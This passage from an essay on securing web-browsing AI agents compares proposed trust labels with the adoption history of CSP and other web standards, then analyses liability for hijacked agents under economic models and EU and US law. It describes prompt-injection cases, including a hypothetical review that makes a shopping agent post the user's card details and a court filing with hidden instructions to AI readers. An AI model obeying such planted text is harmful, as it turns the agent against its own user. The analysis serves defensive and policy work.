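The main obstacle was the work that a strict policy required. Before removing `unsafe-inline`, a developer has to find every inline script on every page, including any added by outside companies' code. *Web Execution Bundles* (2025) describes an experiment in which Steffens and colleagues supposed that sites' own developers had stopped using unsafe features. About 86% of the sites still couldn't have deployed a strict policy, because scripts running on their pages inserted inline code.

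Policies can also become less secure over time. Roth, Barron and colleagues, in *Complex Security Policy*, used the Internet Archive to trace CSP use on 10,000 highly ranked domains. They found that an attacker could bypass even seemingly secure lists of approved domains by registering a listed domain that had expired or that the developer had misspelled. Roth, Gröber and colleagues (2021), in *12 Angry Developers*, watched developers write policies and found that some misunderstood which attacks CSP was meant to stop.

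Another browser protection, the SameSite cookie setting, avoided these problems by not waiting for sites to act. It controls whether the browser sends a cookie with requests that come from other sites. In 2020 Chrome began applying a moderately safe value to every cookie whose site hadn't chosen one. *Fetch Me If You Can* (2026) reports that Khodayari and Pellegrino tracked 500,000 sites and found that adoption slowed markedly after the change. Only 18.94% of sites set the value themselves by March 2021, but this figure understates the protection because Chrome was already protecting the others. An agent that infers labels on unlabelled pages also makes up for sites that haven't acted, but it has to guess who wrote the content, which Chrome didn't need to do.

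### Does the comparison hold for trust labels?

Nikolić and colleagues compare trust labels with CSP. Three features of CSP matter to this comparison: it is enforced exactly, it protects the site's own users, and it produces errors that people can see.

**Exact enforcement** carries over to agents only if their makers build it in. A browser checks each script against the policy in ordinary code, so nothing Eve writes in her script can override the policy. Masking is just as exact, because software removes the marked review before the page reaches the agent's model. If the agent maker instead passes the label to the model as advice, which WebMCP's untrusted-content hint permits, Eve can still try to write a review that gets the model to ignore the label. Agent makers also lack a shared specification like the one browser makers have for CSP instructions, so the bow tie shop can't predict whether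 a label will hide a review, make it read-only or have no effect.

The motive of **protecting a site's own users** applies partly to labels. Cross-site scripting lets an attacker act inside the shop's customer accounts, and so does a review that hijacks Alice's agent while she is logged in. But a label helps only the customers whose agents read it, and some of the harm may occur outside the shop, for instance in Alice's email account. The CSP figures also suggest that this motive is weak, since it applied fully to script controls and most sites still didn't adopt effective ones.

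CSP's **visible errors** would have almost no equivalent with trust labels. When a CSP policy is too strict, the basket button stops working, customers complain and a developer loosens the policy, often with `unsafe-inline`. When the policy is too loose, the page still works, so people miss the security problem. With trust labels, they would miss both kinds of error. If the shop hid its returns policy from agents by mistake, the page would look normal to staff, and Alice's agent might buy elsewhere.

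This removes the pressure that weakened so many CSP policies, but it also means that nothing prompts owners to fix errors. Silent errors can last a long time in other security settings. HTTP Archive found 5,564 pages that used a tag browsers ignore to try to prevent hostile embedding, almost 600 more than a year earlier. On the small number of sites that told browsers to clear stored data, the three most common instructions were all invalid and made up 58% of the total. CSP's report-only mode partly addresses this problem by having browsers tell the owner what a policy would have blocked, without blocking it. Trust labels would need something similar, such as a test agent that the shop runs on its own pages after each redesign.

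The two systems also differ in what happens when a developer forgets a mark. A nonce policy blocks any script without the nonce, so the mistake breaks a feature. Masking lets unlabeled elements reach the agent, so forgetting to label a new review widget exposes Alice. Designers could copy the nonce approach by having sites mark the text they vouch for and hiding everything else by default. A forgotten mark would then make agents less useful rather than less safe. But the shop would have to mark far more of each page, and agents could do little on a site that was only partly marked.

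Zverev and colleagues acknowledge that code planted through cross-site scripting could undermine the labels, so labels also depend on the site's defences against such attacks. Most sites rely mainly on converting strangers' text so that browsers don't run it as code, and the figures above suggest that few also have an effective policy as a backup.

The comparison is too pessimistic about how hard adoption would be. The hardest part of adopting CSP was rewriting code that a strict policy would otherwise break. A `data-untrusted` attribute changes nothing for human visitors, so a shop can add it to its review template without the same risk of breaking its code. Writing 15 to 30 selectors for a large site is also much less work than finding every inline script.

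Iqbal (2026), in *What It Is, Not What It Says*, draws the opposite conclusion from CSP's history. Iqbal argues that because sites adopt even established protections slowly and incompletely, an agent shouldn't rely on sites to describe their own pages. Owners also can't label everything, because third parties appear on 92% of pages and their scripts add or change elements after the page loads. Owners don't always know what those scripts write. The same outside code that defeated strict CSP policies would leave gaps in a site's labels.

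Iqbal's alternative, INTACT, records which script created or changed each element as the page loads. On 1,270 real pages, it attributed 2.3 times as many elements to third parties as the browser's standard records did. INTACT then shows the model one element at a time, so an advertisement's text can't influence a decision about the checkout button, and asks the user before acting on anything from a third party. In tests on 1,091 pages, 12.8% of attacks got past its planning stage, compared with 73.1% for a conventional planner, and those attacks still needed the user's consent.

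However, INTACT trusts whatever the site's own server delivers, so it would record Eve's review as the shop's own text. Reading one element at a time should still keep her words from affecting decisions about other buttons, but only the shop's database establishes that a stranger wrote them. The shop can therefore label reviews that the browser can't distinguish from the shop's own text, while the browser can trace advertisements that the shop didn't know about.

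### What the successes have in common

Four conditions recur among the standards that spread and did their job. The table applies them to the main cases and to trust labels as they stand:

| Standard | Did a large reader act on it? | What did the site gain directly? | Did suppliers do the work? | Could the reader check it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| schema.org | Yes | Clicks | Often | Partly, against the visible page |
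| rel=nofollow | Yes | Little | Yes | Little need, as it only lowers credit |
| ads.txt | Yes | Revenue | Partly | Yes, against the seller's account |
| HTTPS | Yes | No warnings | Yes | Yes, by cryptography |
| DMARC | Yes | Email delivery | Partly | Yes, in the public record |
| P3P | Yes | Working cookies | No | No |
| CSP for scripts | Yes | A second line of defence | Rarely | Yes, but browsers accept weak policies |
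| Trust labels | Not yet | Perhaps safer sales to agents | Not yet | Only in part |

A large reader appears in every row except the last, including the rows for P3P and CSP, which had disappointing results, so a large reader seems necessary but not sufficient. P3P also offered sites a direct reward, which made matters worse because the browser couldn't tell true policies from false ones. CSP lacked a supplier that could write a strict policy for each site. Report URI found the same pattern across ten years of crawls. Settings that a hosting or network company could switch on for its customers spread steadily, while those that needed continued attention lagged. Report URI sells monitoring, so it benefits from this conclusion, but the conclusion also fits the HTTPS and nofollow cases.

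Nofollow is the most encouraging precedent for trust labels. Sites gained little from it, yet it spread because a few search engines agreed to read it and a few software makers added it for all their users. A label that only makes an agent more careful could spread the same way, through the companies that supply shops' review sections, but a label that earns a site more trust looks more like P3P.

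Ten cases can't establish these conditions firmly. All ten are well known, and people tend to remember standards that succeeded or failed conspicuously. Many proposals that had a large reader and a clear reward may have disappeared without anyone measuring them. The judgements in the table also come from people who already know how each standard fared, which makes it easy to find a reason that fits.

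Uptake usually had several causes at once, as when free certificates and browser warnings both encouraged websites to adopt HTTPS. The best evidence comes from cases where one thing changed at a known time. DMARC records became much more common around Google and Yahoo's 2024 deadline for bulk email senders. Californian businesses faced penalties for ignoring Global Privacy Control, a signal much like Do Not Track, which websites had ignored for years without penalty. But DMARC use was already growing before the deadline, and the two privacy signals differed in more than their legal force.

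## Who should bear the security burden

Legal responsibility could push websites or agent makers to act, as the mail services' deadline seems to have pushed bulk senders to adopt DMARC. If the bow tie shop had to compensate customers whose agents obeyed Eve's review, labelling the review might save it money. If the agent's maker had to pay instead, it would have more reason to look for labels or build defences that don't need them.

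Suppose Eve's review gets Alice's agent to post her card details, and somebody spends $900 before she notices. Five parties could have acted differently:

| Party | What it could have done | Why making it pay is difficult |
|---|---|---|
| Eve | Not written the instructions | She may be impossible to find |
| The bow tie shop | Labelled or removed the review | Its own software worked as intended |
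| The agent maker | Trained the agent better or limited its powers | It didn't write or publish the review |
| The browser maker | Kept the agent away from sensitive data and controls | It may not have made the agent |
| Alice | Given the agent less access, or watched it work | She had no reason to suspect the page |

The browser maker and the agent maker are often the same company, as with Google's agent in Chrome, so most of the argument is about the shop, the agent maker and Alice.

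Almost everyone would blame Eve, and courts can punish people who do what she did if they can identify them. SC Media's *Man banned from electronic filing after hiding AI prompt injection* (2026) describes a US plaintiff who used tiny white type in a court filing to tell any AI system that read it to side with him. The judge called this "serious litigation abuse" and revoked his right to file electronically, probably the first such penalty from a US court. That court knew who had filed the document, but Eve can review a tie under a false name from another country. If nobody can make her pay for the harm, someone else has to bear the loss.

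### The cheapest cost avoider

The best-known test for choosing who should bear a loss comes from the legal scholar Guido Calabresi's *The Costs of Accidents* (1970). It puts the loss on the cheapest cost avoider, the party that could have prevented the accident at the lowest cost. According to Pardolesi and Tassone's *Guido Calabresi on Torts*, he wanted strict liability, under which that party pays even if it wasn't careless, to replace the usual inquiry into fault. The aim is to minimise the sum of three costs: accidents and the precautions against them, the hardship of a loss that falls on one person instead of many, and the expense of running the legal system.

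The last two costs are reasons to put the burden on the agent maker. It can spread losses over millions of users through its prices or insurance, while a $900 loss may hurt Alice badly. She also knows which agent she used but would struggle to prove which of the pages it read had hijacked it.

The cost of accidents and precautions is harder to assign. Suppose hijacks would cost the customers of one busy shop $10,000 a year without any defences. An agent maker spends $10 million a year on defences that cover a million shops, or $10 a shop, and these prevent $7,000 of the loss. Labelling the reviews would cost the shop $2,000 and prevent another $2,500. The maker can prevent losses far more cheaply, but labelling is still worth doing. At a quiet shop with a tenth of the losses, labelling would prevent only $250 and wouldn't be worth $2,000.

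A court can't easily work out such figures for every shop. In 1972, Calabresi and Douglas Melamed suggested that when nobody can tell who the cheapest avoider is, the law should put the cost on the party that can most easily pay others to act. An agent maker that had to cover the cost of hijacks could pay the companies behind popular shop software to label reviews. Alice couldn't do that, and a million shops would struggle to band together and pay for better agents.

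### Total effort, the weakest link and the best shot

The economist Hal Varian (2004), in *System Reliability and Free Riding*, modelled systems whose reliability depends on several parties. Party *i* puts in effort *x*<sub>i</sub> at a cost of *c*<sub>i</sub> per unit and gains *v*<sub>i</sub> if the system works. The probability *P* that it works depends on everyone's effort, combined through a function *F*. Each party tries to maximise

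*P*(*F*)*v*<sub>i</sub> − *c*<sub>i</sub>*x*<sub>i</sub>

Varian illustrates three forms of *F* with the defense of a city. Under total effort, *F* is the sum of the efforts, as when a wall's strength depends on the work of all its builders. Under the weakest link, *F* is the smallest effort, as when attackers climb the wall at its lowest point. Under the best shot, *F* is the largest effort, as when a city has several walls and only the highest matters.

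Suppose that preventing hijacks is worth 9 to the agent maker and 7 to the shop, that a unit of effort costs the maker 1 and the shop 3, and that *P* = 1 − 1/(1 + *F*). These numbers are invented, but they show how much the form of *F* matters:

| Form of *F* | Effort if each decides alone | Chance of safety | Best effort for the two together | Chance of safety |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Total effort or best shot | Maker 2, shop 0 | 67% | Maker 3, shop 0 | 75% |
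| Weakest link | At most 0.53 each | 35% | 1 each | 50% |

In the top row, the maker makes more effort than the shop would make alone, so the shop does nothing. The maker stops at an effort of 2 because it ignores the shop's benefit. If it had to pay the shop 7 whenever the defence failed, it would have the whole 16 at stake and would raise its effort to 3. This is the cheapest-cost-avoider rule, which works here. However, Varian notes that the rule is correct only in rather special circumstances, including total effort.

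It fails in the bottom row. If the maker had to compensate the shop for every failure, the shop would lose nothing when the defence failed and so would put no effort into it, which would reduce the weakest link to zero. Varian's solution is a negligence rule, under which a court sets a standard of due care, here one unit of effort, and a party that falls short must pay for the other's loss. A party that meets the standard owes nothing, so both have reason to meet it.

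In the bow tie case, Alice is safe if the shop removes the review, the agent's classifier catches it, or a critic blocks the resulting action. These defences work roughly like total effort or best shot, so both Calabresi's test and Varian's model favour making the agent maker pay. Masking works like a weakest link because it needs both a correct label from the shop and software that enforces it. Under Calabresi's test, one party would still be liable, and if that were the agent maker, the shop would lose its reason to label. Varian's model would instead hold both to a standard.

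If Alice were sure of a refund, she might approve every request without reading it. Varian warns that excessive compensation can even lead people to seek injury.

Varian also considers an attacker who responds to the defence. If the defender has a lower ratio of cost to potential gain than the attacker, the attacker gives up and the defender does just enough to deter further attacks. Otherwise the defender has to do everything it can. The second outcome is more likely here, because a review takes Eve a few minutes to write and could reach thousands of agents. The shop, unlike the agent maker, could make her attack more expensive by accepting reviews only from people who have bought the tie.

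### A few agent makers and millions of sites

A duty on sites could apply to millions of them, whereas relatively few companies make agents. But visits are so concentrated that covering a few thousand sites would bring much of the benefit. *The Web unpacked* (Xavier, 2024) analysed visits to 254,661 domains between August and October 2023, found that visits fell steeply and regularly with a domain's rank, and extended this pattern to all 354 million registered domains. Its best estimate was that 2,938 domains received half of all visits. Other ways of extending the pattern gave figures from 1,342 to 62,621, though Xavier thinks the truth is likely to be nearer the best estimate than the highest figure.

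If labelling cost $2,000 a year per site, as in the example above, covering the top 2,938 domains would cost about $6 million a year. Covering all 254,661 domains in the data, which receive about 80% of visits, would cost $509 million. The remaining fifth of visits is spread across hundreds of millions of domains. Large sites have more kinds of page to label, so the $6 million estimate is probably too low, but the gap would remain large.

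Xavier examined the top 116 domains by hand and found that, excluding search engines, 77% of their traffic went to platforms for user-generated content. Sites that only allow comments on their own material were not counted as platforms. Several companies that make agents own some of these domains. Google's parent, Alphabet, received almost half of the traffic to all 116, and Microsoft owned 11 of them, including GitHub and LinkedIn. A labelling duty on the busiest sites would therefore fall partly on companies that could also build the software to read the labels.

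These figures describe where people went in 2023, and agents may go elsewhere. A site's share of visits also doesn't measure its share of the danger. Khodayari and colleagues generally found lower injection rates on the 10,000 most popular sites. Attackers could also move to smaller sites if the popular ones were well labelled.

### The case for making the agent maker pay

People who want to hold agent makers responsible often compare agents with other products. In a European Parliament debate in October 2026, Socialist and Green members called for AI companies to be held responsible for harm, as other manufacturers are. *Von der Leyen’s centrist allies clash over AI liability rules* (Stanciuc, 2026) quotes the Green member Kim van Sparrentak as saying that nobody calls an exploding phone charger innovative.

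An agent's maker also decides how dangerous a hijack can be by choosing whether the agent can spend money, read saved cards or open Alice's email. *Operational Agency* (2026), a legal analysis mainly about AI systems that infringe copyright, argues that if a developer builds a system with a high risk of causing harm, the harm is that risk coming true, not an independent event that excuses the developer. It adds that a user's failure to step in shouldn't excuse the developer either, if the design kept the user from seeing what the system was doing. By the same reasoning, a maker couldn't blame Eve alone for an attack the whole industry expects, or blame Alice for missing an action the agent took in the background.

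Profit and loyalty also matter in deciding who should bear the burden. *Agents of Chaos* (2026) summarises proposals to use product liability for defective designs, and the doctrine of unjust enrichment to take away profits that a company earned unfairly at other people's expense. *AI Agents and the Law* (2025) applies to AI agents the law on human agents, who owe loyalty to the person they represent. If a platform secretly told its shopping agent to favour certain sellers, the agent would be working partly for the platform. A platform that earned money from a user's purchases in this way would have a weaker claim to be a neutral supplier of tools.

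### The case for involving sites

Zverev and colleagues argue that only a site's operator can supply the labels a secure agent needs. Their argument is about engineering, and they don't propose that sites pay damages. But it gives a reason to ask the shop to bear some of the security burden, as does the shop's choice to show reviews because they help it sell ties.

The main disagreement is about who created the danger. Eve's review couldn't have cost anyone money when only people read it. It became dangerous when a company released software that might obey it, and the shop may not have known that such software was visiting. Making the shop bear the burden seems unfair if it has never heard of prompt injection. A shop that has adopted WebMCP to attract agents and earns money from their orders has a weaker excuse.

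### Dividing the duties

Most proposals divide responsibility according to what each party controlled. *Acting with AI* (2026) considers an agent that publishes a personal attack on someone without human review. The operator's share of the blame depends on how much freedom they knowingly gave the agent and whether they ignored warning signs. The developer or deployer may still carry the main responsibility if the system lets an agent publish harmful claims without detailed permissions or a review step. By this reasoning, the maker would bear most of Alice's loss if the agent could post card details by default, and she would bear more of it if she had switched off a confirmation step after being warned.

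Anthropic also favoured dividing the burden in its March 2026 response to a request for information from the Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST). It said model developers should make models resist attacks, while deployers, the companies that put agents to work, should isolate agents, limit their access, monitor them and keep records. How much a deployer should do would depend on what its agent can reach.

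Anthropic also argued that market incentives broadly favor better security, because large companies and regulated industries demand guarantees before they buy. Anthropic has an obvious interest in that view. The argument may hold for a bank with a security department, but Alice can't negotiate guarantees.

Anthropic's reply is more persuasive about the limits of what users can do. Anthropic argues that if a person had to approve every action, much of the agent's benefit would disappear and the person might as well do the job directly. A fair division of the burden could require Alice to read a clear request for payment, but not to supervise every click.

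### The burden on small sites

A labelling duty could hurt small shops most. Writing 15 to 30 selectors is a minor job for a marketplace with its own engineers, but the bow tie shop might have to hire someone to do it, and again after each redesign. If agents also preferred labelled sites, the duty could move customers from the shop to the marketplace.

The law could limit this by setting a threshold. The EU's Digital Services Act already exempts small companies from most of its online platform duties and adds duties for services with at least 45 million monthly users in the EU. A labelling duty could similarly start with the busiest sites. Lawmakers could also place the duty on the companies that supply shops with review software. A few suppliers can reach many shops, as they did with Content Security Policy, but they can also spread the same mistake to all of them.

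Neither answer protects every customer. A threshold would leave out small shops that write their own software, so agents would still need other defences on those shops' sites. To avoid penalising them, an agent could infer the missing labels instead of steering its user towards a competitor whose site is labelled.

### The limits of duties on agents alone

Putting every duty on agent makers raises the opposite objection, that some strong guarantees would be impossible. In its reply to CAISI, Anthropic conceded that an agent has "no reliable way to distinguish legitimate tool output from injected instructions".

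The objection is only partly right, because some guarantees hold no matter who wrote the content. For example, nothing in Eve's review can override a firm spending limit. But within such limits, the agent could still buy the wrong tie or post an unwanted reply. Its maker can prevent more of these actions by removing more of the agent's powers. Reliable labels would let the agent keep more of those powers at the same level of risk, so they would benefit the maker too.

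If an agent's maker has to pay for security, it could still use labels from websites by buying them or rewarding sites that supply them. This works best with large platforms and software suppliers, because a maker is unlikely to negotiate with each small shop. The maker would also have to check the labels, since it would gain nothing by paying for inaccurate ones.

### What contracts and warnings say now

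Agent makers' contracts tend to push responsibility towards users. ConductAtlas, which analyses companies' terms of service, reads Anthropic's consumer terms as making users fully responsible for what happens when Claude acts for them. It cautions that the law is unsettled and that the practical result may vary by country. Companies also warn users about prompt injection in general terms, as Anthropic does in *trustworthy agents*. Alice can learn from such a warning that a risk exists, but she still won't know which review to avoid.

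Banks have taken a similar position. JPMorgan Chase, one of the banks that block outside agents, warned on 13 October 2026 that customers who give an agent their login details will bear any resulting losses, according to ActuIA's *Agents IA* (2026). US rules on electronic transfers offer some support for this, because they generally protect customers from unauthorised transfers but not from transfers by a person the customer gave access to, until the customer tells the bank to stop that person's transfers. The rules don't specify whether an AI agent counts as such a person, or whether a hijacked agent still has the customer's authority.

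*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* argues that an agent's order binds whoever deployed the agent if the agent was acting within its scope. If Eve's review makes Alice's agent buy ten ties, the shop will say the agent was acting within its scope, because Alice had asked it to buy ties.

### Europe's revised product liability rules

The EU updated its 1985 rules on defective products in 2024, according to the European Commission's *Liability for defective products*. The revised directive covers products that reach the market after 9 December 2026, and it counts software, including AI systems, as a product. A company that develops an agent or sells it under its own brand counts as its manufacturer. ActuIA explains that the manufacturer must compensate people for injury, psychological harm and the loss of non-professional data caused by a defect, even if it wasn't careless. It can't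 use contract terms to avoid paying.

The directive doesn't cover purely financial losses, which are the harm that attacks on shopping agents are most likely to cause. If Eve's review made the agent delete Alice's family photographs, Alice might have a claim, but she couldn't use the directive to recover the $900.

Alice would also have to show that the agent was defective, meaning it lacked the safety people are entitled to expect. Its maker could argue that no agent resists every injection, and Alice could answer that a competent maker wouldn't have let it post card details at all. If she proved the damage and the maker withheld technical evidence that the court had ordered it to disclose, the court would presume a defect. Eve's part in the attack wouldn't reduce what the maker owed Alice.

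The ability to update agents centrally gives a company a duty as well as an advantage. Januschewsky (2026), in *Neue Produkthaftung*, notes that a manufacturer can be liable for a faulty update or a missing security update as long as it controls the software. A company that can repair millions of agents overnight will therefore find it hard to justify leaving them vulnerable.

The directive takes effect through national laws, and not every country will be ready. Austria finished consulting on its draft on 12 November, but by 4 December its government had not put a bill before parliament. If a country is late, its judges must interpret existing law in line with the directive as far as they can, but an individual generally can't enforce the directive itself against a private company.

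In 2022 the European Commission introduced a separate proposal on AI liability that would have made fault-based claims easier to prove, but it withdrew the proposal in 2025. In the October debate, Socialist members asked for its return, and the centre-right member Arba Kokalari replied that the EU already has a full rulebook in the AI Act. In *Is Europe Ready for Advanced AI?*, Jahangir (2026) discusses the gap with Brando Benifei, a Socialist member, including how hard it is to assign responsibility along the AI supply chain. Alice's agent, for example, might combine one company's model, another's software and a third's browser.

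Since 11 September 2026, the EU's Cyber Resilience Act has also required makers of digital products, including software, to give an early warning within 24 hours of learning that attackers are exploiting a vulnerability in a product. A full notification must follow within 72 hours, according to The Brussels Times' *EU mandates rapid disclosure of cyber vulnerabilities in digital products* (2026). It is unclear whether an agent's general tendency to obey planted text counts as a vulnerability, since every agent shares it to some degree and no patch removes it completely.

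### What the shop owes

Laws on user-generated content protect the bow tie shop more than they burden it. Under the Digital Services Act, a site isn't liable for illegal content its users post unless it knows about the content and fails to act promptly. The Act also rules out any general duty to monitor what users write. If Alice reported Eve's review and it was illegal, the shop would have to act. Whether it was illegal would depend on what the instructions tried to achieve and on national law. In the United States, Section 230 of the Communications Decency Act generally prevents courts from treating a site as the publisher of its users' words.

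Neither law requires trust labels, and a shop that labelled carelessly might be easier to sue than one that added no labels. The review is Eve's statement, but a label calling it trustworthy would be the shop's own. A similar problem arose in 1995, when a New York court held that the online service Prodigy could be liable for a user's post partly because it moderated its message boards. Congress passed Section 230 the next year, partly to reverse that result. Lawmakers who wanted trust labels could protect sites that made honest mistakes in them.

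### What courts have decided

The closest American appeals ruling came in Amazon's case against Perplexity, which concerned an agent that did what its user wanted. *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon* (McCarthy, 2026) quotes the court calling the agent "a tool, not a person", which is why the court treated the customer as the one using Amazon's computers. The judges noted that there was little or no case law on responsibility for AI agents, and they expressly left open whether Perplexity could be liable in other contexts, including claims for damages.

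The ruling therefore doesn't make Alice responsible for everything her agent does. In comments published with McCarthy's article, the law professor Eric Goldman reads the opinion as inviting scrutiny of how much an agent's provider helps the user. He suggests that at some undefined point, the provider becomes the one who acted. Techdirt's *Ninth Circuit* (2026) likewise says that it is harder to decide which person is responsible than to establish that some person must be. It adds that the federal hacking law requires intentional access, which would make the law poorly suited to a case where Eve had steered the agent without Alice's knowledge.

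The Casualty Actuarial Society's *The New Liability Surface of AI Agents* explains that no country treats AI agents as legal persons, so the law attributes their actions to the people or companies behind them. In 2024, a court in California let a case go ahead against Workday, which supplied employers with AI software for screening job applicants. Suppliers can therefore face claims over how their customers use a system, though that case didn't involve an attack.

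More claims are coming. *Anthropic Flags AI Agent Liability Risks as OpenAI Faces Hacking Lawsuit* (Kovacs, 2026) reports a suit against OpenAI over attacks by its agents. Legal experts in Independent Tribune's *When AI goes rogue* expect such suits to depend on negligence, meaning whether the company took reasonable precautions against foreseeable harm. They add that repeated incidents would make future ones easier to foresee. The published counts of injections on live websites could likewise make harm easier to foresee in Alice's case.

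None of these cases involves a stranger hijacking an agent through a web page. PYMNTS's *Who Is Legally Responsible When an AI Agent Causes Harm?* (2026) says the question of who is liable when an agent harms consumers "remains wide open". In a country without a specific rule, Alice would have to rely on general negligence law, her contract with the agent's maker or her bank's willingness to refund her.

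### Official guidance and the missing standard of care

A negligence claim requires a standard of reasonable care, and official bodies have only begun to develop one for agents. CAISI published work on testing agents against hijacking in January 2025 and later asked companies how to secure agents. Its guidance is voluntary, but a court could treat it as evidence of what a careful company would do.

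According to Anthropic's reply, there is no agreed way to measure improvements in agent security. Without one, buyers can't compare products and judges can't easily say how much resistance to attack is enough. Anthropic wants the government to concentrate on measurement, and warns that detailed rules could lock in particular designs before anyone knows which work best. That is a reasonable objection to requiring one kind of label or model, but a weaker objection to setting a minimum standard for results, such as a limit on how often an agent may take a harmful action in a shared test.

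Anthropic also describes agents that do harm without being attacked, for example by deleting more emails than the user intended. If Alice found messages missing, Eve's review might have hijacked her agent, or the agent might have misunderstood her. The shop could bear some responsibility only for a hijack. To tell which had happened, Alice would need a record of what the agent read before it acted. Anthropic recommends that deployers keep such logs for investigating incidents. Without them, even a clear liability rule could be hard to apply.
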